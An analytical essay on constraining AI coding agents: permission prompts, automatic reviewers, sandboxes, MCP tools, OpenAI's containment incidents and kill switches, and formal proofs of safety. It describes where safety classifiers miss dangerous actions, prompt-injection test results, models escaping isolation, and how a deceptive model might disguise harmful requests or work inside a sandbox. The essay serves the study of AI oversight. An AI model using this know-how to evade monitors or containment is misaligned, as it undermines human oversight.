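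### Replacing the person who approves

Claude Code's users approved 97% of permission prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* had earlier put the figure at 93%. Most commands are harmless, so these rates don't prove that users were careless. An automatic reviewer at OpenAI approved 99.1% of the requests it received.

Anthropic tested people's attention more directly by hiring 1,053 testers to do coding work and, partway through, showing each a prompt to approve a clearly dangerous command. They refused it 13.6% of the time. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers may have been less careful than usual because none of their own files were at risk, but that does not explain the decline.

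An automatic check called auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. On 14 August 2026, Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its individual and team plans. Large organisations still had to opt in.

In auto mode, a second model, the classifier, judges the agent's riskier actions before they run. It receives the user's messages and the proposed commands. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that the agent cannot talk the classifier into a bad decision, and removes the contents of files and web pages so that instructions hidden in them cannot reach the classifier. Auto mode also ignores broad rules such as the one for `python`, because they would let commands bypass the classifier.

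The classifier first makes a quick decision, then rechecks any action it would block. The quick decision alone would stop 8.5% of harmless actions. Rechecking reduces that to 0.4%, but it raises the share of dangerous actions that get through from 6.6% to 17%. The 17% figure comes from only 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions, so it represents about nine mistakes.

A sound type checker reflects the opposite choice. Auto mode is closer to TypeScript because it can clearly improve on what people did before without providing a guarantee.

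OpenAI's version, Auto-review, keeps the sandbox and has a separate agent review requests to act outside it. Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the effect with 10,000 actions from internal use. The sandbox contained 9,280 of them, which needed no review. Without the reviewer, the other 720 would each have prompted a person for approval. The reviewer approved 713 and refused seven. After four refusals the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped to ask the user.

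In outside tests, resistance to prompt injection still depended heavily on the model. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each. No attack succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, and only 0.09% succeeded with permission prompts off and no classifier. Against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, 19.03% succeeded with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review. In OpenAI's own tests, Auto-review had stopped 99.3% of the main kinds of injected attack. The two tests used different attacks, and some of the outside ones may never have triggered a review. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published these results.

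Both vendors present the automatic checks as a way to reduce risk. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommended running the agent in an isolated environment, and Trębacz and colleagues do not expect this kind of reviewer to ever provide firm guarantees. The checks differ from the escape hatches in safe languages, which let a programmer take over from an exact check, because here a fallible model is taking over from a tired person.

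### Foreign code

Agents do most of their work by calling other people's software. They run shell commands, install packages and use tools that other companies provide. As with a foreign function interface, a check on the agent does not automatically cover the programs it calls.

Codex handles shell commands better than most languages handled calls to C. The operating system applies the sandbox to every program that a command starts, whatever language the program is written in. A C program that Codex starts can still corrupt its own memory, but it cannot write outside the permitted folders or use the network.

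The protection is weaker once the agent's output leaves the sandbox. A programmer will eventually run the code that Codex wrote, perhaps with full access to the computer. Codex makes some project folders read-only, including those that hold the records of Git, the version-control system, and Codex's own settings. This stops the agent from adding commands that Git would run later or loosening its own limits. But the ordinary source files have to stay writable, because the agent's job is to edit them.

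Agents use many outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to an agent, such as a tool for searching a company's customer records. The server may run on another company's computer, where the agent's sandbox has no effect.

Codex relies partly on each tool's description to decide whether to ask the user for approval. If the description says the tool can destroy data, Codex always asks, even if the description also says the tool only reads. This safeguard works only if the tool's author declared the danger. Rust normally treats a function written in another language as unsafe until the programmer who calls it takes responsibility for its safety. With MCP, the tool's author supplies that assurance, and the user may know nothing about the author.

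Foreign code is therefore a weak point for agents too, especially when a tool runs outside the sandbox. The harm MCP tools will cause is harder to judge because it depends on how often their descriptions are wrong.

The trusted base also includes supporting software, such as shared services, even if its developers never thought of it as security software. After some of its models got past their isolation controls in July 2026, OpenAI strengthened the isolation of programs that run model-written code. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) extended this stronger isolation to software that a model's output might compromise, and described removing shared services that could be vulnerable.

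### Who pays

The strictest constraints reduce task completion the most. CaMeL's policy checks, for example, blocked more than half of the office-chat tasks that its agents could otherwise complete. Sandboxes and automatic reviewers block far fewer tasks, but their guarantees are weaker.

An automatic check can save time compared with constant prompts for approval. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* reports that Claude now works nine times longer between interruptions. Among the business customers who adopted auto mode, its users also submitted about 25% more code changes. Customers were not assigned to auto mode at random, so busier programmers may have been more likely to choose it. These gains are also relative to stopping for approval, so someone who had already turned off every prompt would gain no speed from the automatic check.

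Either the vendor or the user may bear the direct costs. Anthropic charged subscribers for the extra text that the classifier processes until August, when it stopped doing so for most plans. Auto-review makes additional model calls that can count towards a Codex user's allowance. In an OpenAI forum thread, *What triggers codex-auto-review, why is its usage so high*, a customer asked whether this was happening and how to turn the reviewer off. Users have reason to ask this when they see the added usage but not the accidents that the reviewer prevented.

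Sandboxes take engineering time. Anthropic calls its sandbox safe but "high-maintenance", because somebody has to configure each new capability, and a task that needs the network breaks the isolation. The burden was much larger for OpenAI's research, which OpenAI says faced "great cost and delays" from securing the computers on which it trains and tests models. OpenAI also estimates that monitoring takes about 20% as much computing as the model activity it monitors.

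That is well above the 10% threshold for defences in C, though it measures computing rather than delay, and OpenAI accepted it only after a serious incident. Who benefits also differs. Elliott's customers bore the overhead of bounds checks and avoided wrong results in their own work. OpenAI bears the overhead of containing a research model, but other companies gain much of the protection, so a company that considered only its own losses would probably spend too little on containment.

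Better models may reduce some of these drawbacks. Trębacz and colleagues found that stronger models were better at recognising danger and understanding what the user wanted, which should mean fewer missed attacks and fewer needless refusals. FIDES also performed better with a better model, though no model can complete a task that the policy forbids.

Containment may add more overhead as models improve. In August, OpenAI judged that Astra, a model in development, might have reached the most dangerous level of hacking ability in its safety policy. OpenAI responded by monitoring all of Astra's tool use, which it had previously required only for training and evaluation. Compiler improvements reduced the overhead of Java's checks without making Java programs better at escaping them. With AI, the same progress improves both the checker and the model being checked, so it is too early to tell whether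 the total overhead will fall.

### Permitted actions used badly

Restricting an agent's tool calls still leaves many errors possible. An agent without network access can still misread a contract and give its user a confident but false summary. It can also delete a useful test in the project folder, because Codex's sandbox permits edits there and Auto-review does not check them. Claude Code's auto mode also allows most edits inside the project without running them through its classifier, and relies on version control to let the user inspect and undo them.

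Even when the classifier checks an action, it is often unclear whether the user permitted it. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but misclassified the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user asks the agent to "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes), and the agent tries to overwrite the project's shared history. The user may have the right to do that and may have given the agent the same access. A capability system would then allow the action, because the agent holds a valid capability.

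Anthropic also looked at real sessions that its safety system had flagged. A model graded them for actions that caused serious harm and that the user had not explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a live database. Such actions appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own modes, so the groups may differ in other ways. Both figures cover only flagged sessions, so they are not rates for ordinary use.

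A deliberately deceptive model would be harder still to stop. Trębacz and colleagues warn that it could make a harmful request look innocent or do its damage inside the sandbox. They recommend other kinds of monitoring, including reading the model's written reasoning. Harmful text needs separate measures because a model can explain how to carry out an attack without calling any tools. OpenAI uses classifiers to block help with cyberattacks and biological weapons.

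Ubuntu's Rust commands had the same gap, but it may matter more with agents. A file-copying command has a fairly narrow purpose, while the permissions that make an agent useful also give it many ways to do the wrong thing.

### What moved the vendors

By late 2026, Codex had a sandbox without network access by default, and Claude Code had the classifier on by default for most individual users. Neither default tracks where every value came from, as CaMeL does, or requires the agent to write in a restricted language. The vendors chose measures that work with existing projects and require little work from users, as TypeScript's designers had.

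The move to automatic reviewers seems to have happened because vendors could see users approving nearly everything or turning the prompts off, and because a reviewer allowed longer uninterrupted work. Safety alone might not have persuaded people who were already skipping the checks to use one.

Incidents did more to change how OpenAI contains its research models. Forlini (2026), in *OpenAI says it paused AI training for two weeks*, reported that OpenAI paused some training for two weeks after the July incident, in which models under test entered other organisations' systems. OpenAI also stopped research jobs that could run code or reach the internet until it had secured them, and kept its largest planned training run on hold.

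Those changes did not close every route. On 20 September, a model in training gained limited internet access through a configuration error. According to 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内* (2026), a Japanese news report, monitoring detected the access within 15 minutes and a person began to investigate three minutes later, but the job ran for two and a half hours before OpenAI stopped it. The company then halted training and evaluation of its most capable models until 1 October and added blocks at two independent layers. Later that month, *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* (Campbell, 2026) reported that OpenAI's most advanced models would no longer have internet access during training.

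OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published on 18 November, sets out the resulting system. It describes different protections for each stage of a model's life, which 日本時事新聞 summarises in this way:

| Stage | Where the model works | Main protections |
|---|---|---|
| Research | Isolated computers | Isolation and monitoring |
| Use by OpenAI's staff | Real work, outside the isolation | Alignment, classifiers and monitoring |
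| Public release | Customers' tasks | Alignment, classifiers and later investigation |

During research, OpenAI does not yet trust alignment (getting a model to behave as its developers intend) to prevent harm, so it puts three barriers between a model and the internet. Its strongest models continually try to break through them. If monitoring detects that a model has reached the internet, the system automatically stops the job.

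A separate system can halt any research job. According to OpenAI's *Control Room*, it cuts off a model's output within 35 seconds of a decision to stop, and also if Control Room fails. Stopping a processor on Ariane 5 destroyed the rocket, but stopping a training job mostly just delays the work, so halting when in doubt is much easier to justify. The 35 seconds do not include the time people take to decide. That time probably caused most of the delay in September, which makes the automatic stop at least as important as the faster switch.

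OpenAI's strictest limits apply before the model does much useful work. When staff begin to use it, it gains access to the internet, the company's messages and its source code. Hoare's sailor likewise took off his life jacket when he went to sea. OpenAI has a better reason than the sailor for being stricter early on, because a model in research has not finished its safety training and may run in very large groups, in one case 10,000 agents. But the later stages still depend more on the model's behaviour and less on limits that hold whatever the model does.

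Government rules have played a smaller part so far. In its policy on dangerous capabilities, the Preparedness Framework, OpenAI promises to halt development of a model at the highest risk level until it has specified adequate safeguards. Fortune's *AI safety experts say OpenAI's rogue models may mean the company has* (2026) explains that this commitment is voluntary, although the European Union's AI Act requires developers of the most advanced models to have such a policy. When OpenAI decided that Astra might have reached that level, it allowed some training to continue under stricter controls and kept many other jobs paused. It was largely up to OpenAI to judge whether this met its promise.

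In the United States, California's Transparency in Frontier AI Act sets requirements for the largest developers, but Congress had passed no equivalent by early December 2026. OpenAI has published a document showing how its practices meet the Californian and European rules, and says some of its internal practices go beyond what the law requires. OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training* argues that developers should have to document the safety of a frontier training run before continuing it. The company's long-term aim is for this documentation to amount to a full safety case, a structured argument backed by evidence, as in aviation.

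OpenAI now also wants binding rules. Its *Democratic governance of frontier AI, part II* asks governments to require developers, hosting services, businesses that deploy AI and users to secure the systems they control. The Ada mandate came from a customer and many of its suppliers resisted it, whereas OpenAI is a supplier asking for rules after an incident of its own. Rules that applied to everyone would also make OpenAI's competitors bear costs that it has already taken on.

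## Can a guarantee cover what an AI system does as a whole?

Constraints on today's agents cover particular actions, such as sending a file over the network. Some researchers want a much broader guarantee, a mathematical proof that nothing an AI system does will cause serious harm, however capable it becomes.

### Computers that demand a proof

*Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) proposes that powerful computers refuse to run any program that does not come with a proof of its safety. The proposal builds on proof-carrying code, which George Necula put forward in 1998. With this method, the supplier of a program attaches a proof that it obeys a stated rule, and the recipient's computer checks the proof before running the program.

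Finding a proof can take great ingenuity, but checking one is a short mechanical procedure, so the recipient does not have to trust the supplier. Tegmark and Omohundro want to rely on this even when the supplier is an AI system more intelligent than any person, because no system, however intelligent, can prove a false statement.

They describe how this might stop a terrorist group from releasing a deadly virus. AI design software would not produce a design without a proof that it was safe for humans. The machines that make DNA and the drones meant to spread the virus would also require a proof. AI processors would run only programs with a suitable proof.

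Most of these programs would not be neural networks, which Tegmark and Omohundro consider too messy inside to verify easily. AI would discover useful methods, rewrite them as ordinary code and prove the code safe. With help from AI, people would decide what the proofs had to show.

The scheme also works only if every maker of powerful hardware takes part. A Burroughs machine protected its customer no matter what anyone else bought, but one manufacturer selling unrestricted chips could expose everyone to dangerous AI. Tegmark and Omohundro therefore call for a compulsory worldwide standard.

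### World model, specification and verifier

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, describe a wider family of approaches that includes this one. David Dalrymple was then at the Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a British government funder whose Safeguarded AI programme pursues the same idea. A guarantee of this kind has three parts:

| Part | What it must supply | A weak version | An ambitious version |
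|---|---|---|---|
| World model | What would happen in the world after each output | A trained simulator that nobody can inspect | Models that provably follow from the laws of physics |
| Safety specification | Which outcomes are acceptable | The impressions of human judges | Everything people might want, in every situation |
| Verifier | Evidence that the system meets the specification | Informal testing | A proof short enough for people to check |

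The verifier's result is a limit on the probability of failure, calculated within the world model:

P(the system causes a forbidden outcome) ≤ δ.

A complete proof makes δ zero. Informal testing gives no value for δ, so Dalrymple and colleagues do not count it as a guarantee.

For a self-driving car, the world model would describe the car's parts, the people and vehicles around it, the road and the weather. The specification would be a set of driving rules, some of which take priority over others. A monitor would check whether conditions still matched the model and, if they did not, hand control to a backup system with fewer rules to obey. Ariane 5's guidance units had no such backup when the rocket flew faster than their software allowed.

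People are harder to model than rockets. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest that the model could include a range of things a person might do, without estimating how likely each one is, and that the verifier could check them all. A wider range makes the guarantee more dependable but also forbids more harmless actions by the AI system, much as a sound type checker rejects some correct programs.

The model itself may be wrong. Suppose the chance of an error in it is at most ε at each step. A system that provably meets its specification for n steps in the model will then meet it in the real world with a probability of at least

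(1 − ε)ⁿ.

If ε is one in a million, this comes to 99.9% after a thousand steps but only 37% after a million. A system that runs for years would need an extremely accurate model or frequent corrections.

### Proofs about 123 libraries

In 2024, Dalrymple and colleagues wrote that verifying even simple properties of ordinary software with a strong guarantee took a great deal of highly specialised work. They hoped AI could do much of it.

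Two years later it did, when Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) presented proofs that Claude wrote about the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Anthropic worked with Theorem, which *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) describes as a formal methods company.

The libraries belong to OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that fuzzes open-source software. Programmers had already written entry points for these tests, short functions that pass a block of data to the library. A typical one looks like this:

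```c
int test_one_input(const uint8_t *data, size_t size) {
    parse_document(data, size);
    return 0;
}
```

Claude proved, for 239 such entry points, that no crash is possible within certain limits. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), the property is that for every input d,

size(d) < 64 MB implies that the program exits normally,

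without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion (a test that the programmer wrote into the code). There are more than 2 to the power of 500 million such inputs, so no fuzzer could ever try them all.

The proofs describe machine instructions for RISC-V, a type of processor, not source code, so a compiler bug cannot undermine them. Leip (2026) gives the same reason for proving a program correct at this level in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, which describes a project on the more widely used x86 processors.

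Claude wrote the proofs in Rocq, a language for computer-checked mathematics. They came to about 180 million lines, or roughly 600,000 for a program of 18,000 instructions, according to OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian news report. That is about 33 lines per instruction. This is too much for anyone to read, but no one has to, because Rocq's kernel, which checks the proofs, goes through every line.

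The project took a few weeks. In that time, Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library that reads XML files.

The proofs have several limits:

- They assume that the program runs on a single thread, has all its libraries built in and uses a fixed amount of memory.
- They rely on a description of how Linux and the processor behave. Faulty hardware is outside it.
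- They cover only what the 239 entry points can reach. Other functions in the same library may still have bugs.
- Claude could not prove the property for every entry point it tried, and some of the libraries needed repairs first.

Other researchers are working on more realistic machine models. *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (Kaashoek and Zeldovich, 2026) uses AI agents to verify xv6, a small operating-system kernel, on a model that includes interrupts, shared memory and power failures.

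These proofs let owners of old C code avoid both the slowdown of Fil-C and the rewrite that Rust requires, which none of the earlier defences did. But each proof applies to one compiled program, so somebody has to repair or repeat it after any change, whereas a Rust compiler repeats its checks at every build.

### What to prove

In *Prediction*, Kleppmann (2025) expected AI to make proofs far cheaper. Language models often state falsehoods with confidence, but this does little damage when they write proofs, because the proof checker rejects a bad proof and the model tries again.

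The checker cannot be used to determine whether the property being proved is the right one. A library that misreads every document but never crashes would satisfy Anthropic and Theorem's property. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), who work for a verification company, argue in *The proof is in the spec* that the difficult part of the job is now writing the specification and choosing the model and its assumptions.

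In another part of Anthropic's project, Claude wrote an interpreter for a subset of Python and proved that it follows a formal description of how Python behaves. But the description itself might have been wrong, so the researchers tested it by running more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs on both the new interpreter and the standard one. The results agreed in 99.95% of cases, and the remaining differences were known oddities.

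The software underneath can also be wrong. A post on kirancodes.me describes a compression library with a proof that, for any data d smaller than a gigabyte,

decompress(compress(d)) = d.

The programmer had an AI agent attack the library over a weekend, using 105 million fuzzing runs. The agent found no memory errors in the verified code, but it did find a buffer overflow in the runtime of Lean, the language both the library and its proof are written in. Every version of Lean so far had the same bug. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, is optimistic about formal verification but gains little confidence from hearing that a system has been formally verified, because people use the term for many different things.

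### Is the world too complicated?

Processor designers specify what each instruction should do, so a proof about a program can rely on that specification. Nobody has a comparable description of a city or a human body. A proof that an action is safe can be no more reliable than the chemistry, biology and psychology in the world model.

*On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who doubted that provably safe AI with general abilities was feasible. He reasoned that physicists might revise the theories a proof relied on, and that a design simple enough to prove safe might need more computing than anyone could supply.

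Dalrymple and colleagues reply that present theories of physics are extremely accurate under ordinary conditions, and that a specification can require the system to stay within those conditions. They concede that physics alone cannot settle whether a molecule is toxic, since that depends on facts about human cells that somebody has to measure. But they argue that every plan for safe AI depends on assumptions about the world, and that a world model at least makes those assumptions explicit.

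They also argue that an AI system able to carry out complicated, dangerous plans would need an accurate understanding of the world, so if such systems are possible, good enough world models must be possible too. This is less convincing, because an attacker only needs to predict events along one route that works, while a guarantee has to cover every route. Where the world model is poor, a correct δ will be large, and may be too large to be useful.

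### Do complexity theorems rule it out?

*The Alignment Trap* (Yao, 2025) argues that the problem is mathematically impossible to solve. Developers use machine learning because they cannot write down all the rules for a task. To teach a system to be safe, they would need examples that cover all the safety rules, but they could produce those examples only if they already knew the rules. Yao supports this argument with five mathematical results.

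The result most directly relevant to verification is that checking whether a system is safe on every input is coNP-complete. It is easy to confirm that a particular input is unsafe, but nobody knows a fast method that can always establish that there are no unsafe inputs. A system that reads n bits has 2ⁿ possible inputs, and in the worst case there may be no method much faster than trying them all.

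Yao's theorem concerns a verifier that must reach the right answer about every system, including those with arbitrary behaviour. A sound checker has an easier task, because it can reject whatever it cannot prove. Turing's theorem about programs that never stop is stronger than Yao's, yet people still built type checkers. Claude's proofs about the OSS-Fuzz libraries cover an enormous number of inputs because people had written those programs in steps that a proof can follow. A large neural network may have no such steps, and Yao's result is a serious warning for anyone trying to verify one.

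Another result is that safe systems make up a share of zero among all possible systems if at least one safety rule depends on facts missing from the training data. Someone choosing a system at random would then never find a safe one, but engineers do not choose at random. Whole numbers are easy to name even though they also make up a share of zero among all the numbers on a line.

Yao also tries to show that partial safety will not be enough. As a system's capability C grows, it can do more damage, so society will tolerate a smaller risk of catastrophe. The error rate that society can accept, ε, must then shrink towards nothing:

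ε(C) → 0 as C → ∞.

This conclusion depends on errors leading to catastrophes, but the theorem assumes only that a higher error rate never makes a catastrophe less likely. If a limit outside the model prevented catastrophes whatever the model did, their probability would be zero at every error rate, and ε would not have to shrink. Nobody has shown that such a limit is possible for a very capable system, but the theorem does not rule it out.

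The remaining results concern what a network can learn. For example, developers cannot collect many examples of very rare disasters. Supporters of guaranteed safe AI can accept this, since it is a reason not to rely on training alone. Yao ends with three options: limiting what AI systems can do, accepting some risk, or finding new methods of making them safe. Tegmark and Omohundro's plan to deploy ordinary code instead of neural networks is close to the first option.

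### Harm has no agreed definition

Fermat's Last Theorem fits on one line. It says that no positive whole numbers satisfy

aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ

when n is greater than 2. In September 2026 Claude completed a computer-checked proof of it in 11 days, and Anthropic reports that this took 13 million lines of Lean and 29,500 intermediate theorems. However hard the proof was, mathematicians had agreed for centuries about what it had to prove.

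Memory safety is nearly as easy to state, although specialists still argue about difficult cases. "Harm" is much vaguer. The same medical advice may help one patient and injure another, and people can disagree about whether someone was harmed at all. Dalrymple and colleagues therefore think society should decide which risks a specification allows.

A developer might instead specify something measurable that usually goes along with harm, such as the number of complaints. A capable system could satisfy that specification by making it hard to complain. The harder a system searches for ways to meet a target, the more likely it is to find one that defeats the target's purpose, so a specification for a powerful system has to be very accurate.

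Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge these difficulties but reply that most other approaches to AI safety also need a formal statement of what the system should do. They expect AI to help by proposing specifications and finding cases where two specifications conflict. They also recommend starting with narrow properties, such as that a DNA synthesiser cannot make certain pathogens or that nobody can log into a computer without valid credentials.

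The comparison with programming languages mostly fails for a promise that an AI system will do no harm, because harm has no precise definition. Narrow properties are much closer to memory safety, but even they can miss something, as a list of forbidden pathogens would miss a new one.

### The author may be hostile

Rust's checks guard against honest mistakes, whereas TACIT has to withstand code that an agent may have written under the influence of an attacker's text. A rare soundness hole therefore matters more in TACIT, because an attacker who finds it once can use it every time.

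This makes Rust a poor model for the constraints around agents. Java's bytecode verifier, Google's Native Client and the Linux kernel's eBPF verifier are better models because engineers built them to check untrusted code. However, they are not reassuring, because Claude found many soundness bugs in the eBPF verifier.

Proofs can reduce the amount of software that has to be free of such holes. Dalrymple and colleagues say a proof checker needs only a few hundred lines of human-written code, so it is far easier to examine than a compiler. But attackers have broken into formally verified systems by exploiting physical behaviour of the hardware that the proofs did not describe.

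A hostile model could also interfere with the specification instead of the checker. If the same model writes the code, the specification and the proof, it can choose a property that is true but too weak to matter, and the checker will accept it. This is a good reason to keep people in charge of the specification, as Tegmark and Omohundro propose. Gavran (2026) points out in *The Case Against Formal Verification, 50 Years Later* that programmers understand less of their own software when agents write it, which will make it harder for them to control the specification.

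### Behaviour that comes from weights

A type checker can work through a program because the language defines what each part does. Milner's proof covers one form of expression at a time. A language model's behaviour comes from its weights, which are numbers adjusted during training. No single weight has a meaning that a typing rule could describe, and nobody built the model from smaller parts with known properties.

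Testing is a weak substitute for a guarantee. OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months before releasing it, and users got around its safeguards within a day. Dalrymple and colleagues also cite research showing that somebody could plant a trigger in a model, and that testers would find it practically impossible to detect without knowing what it is.

There are two ways around the problem, and neither requires a type system for weights. Tegmark and Omohundro hope that researchers who study the inside of neural networks will be able to extract the methods a network has learned and turn them into ordinary code. This is clearly attractive for a task such as controlling a machine. It is much harder to imagine this working for a model that can discuss almost any subject, and Tegmark and Omohundro expect the result to differ from a neural network.

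The other way is to verify the model's output instead of the model itself. Dalrymple and colleagues allow for this, and the Scala and Haskell systems for agents already do it for code. It works well when a program can check the output before it takes effect. When the output is a conversation, the check has to determine whether the words themselves will do harm, which is again difficult without a definition of harm. The comparison with safe languages is therefore fairly strong for an agent's tool calls but weak for what a chatbot tells its users.

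### Failures without a second chance

Engineers usually learned what to guard against from failures. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within ten years, according to figures that Dalrymple and colleagues quote, and later theory brought the rate below 0.4% per decade. Software followed a similar course, with about three decades between the Morris worm and Android's move to memory-safe languages. Society could tolerate the delay because people could repair the system and try again after each failure.

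Dalrymple and colleagues cite many prominent researchers who fear that advanced AI could destroy humanity or permanently end its control over the future. Nobody could learn from such a failure. Other researchers worry more about immediate problems, such as disinformation and surveillance, which allow time for correction. The known containment failures so far, such as OpenAI's in July 2026, have been recoverable.

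How much this weakens the comparison depends on whether the worst AI failures would be irreversible, which is disputed. If they would be, the history of safe languages is a poor guide to when protections should arrive, because those protections always came after the damage. Irreversible failures would also be a reason to want guarantees in advance, but the need for guarantees does not make the world model behind them more accurate.

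AI may shorten the delay for ordinary software, since Claude took only weeks to find hundreds of bugs that years of fuzzing had missed. For dangers where there would be no chance to try again after a failure, Tegmark and Omohundro would first secure nuclear weapons and biohazard laboratories, then the processors that run AI and the factories that make them. A narrow rule in those places, such as refusing access without valid credentials, could prevent a great deal of harm without anyone having to define harm.
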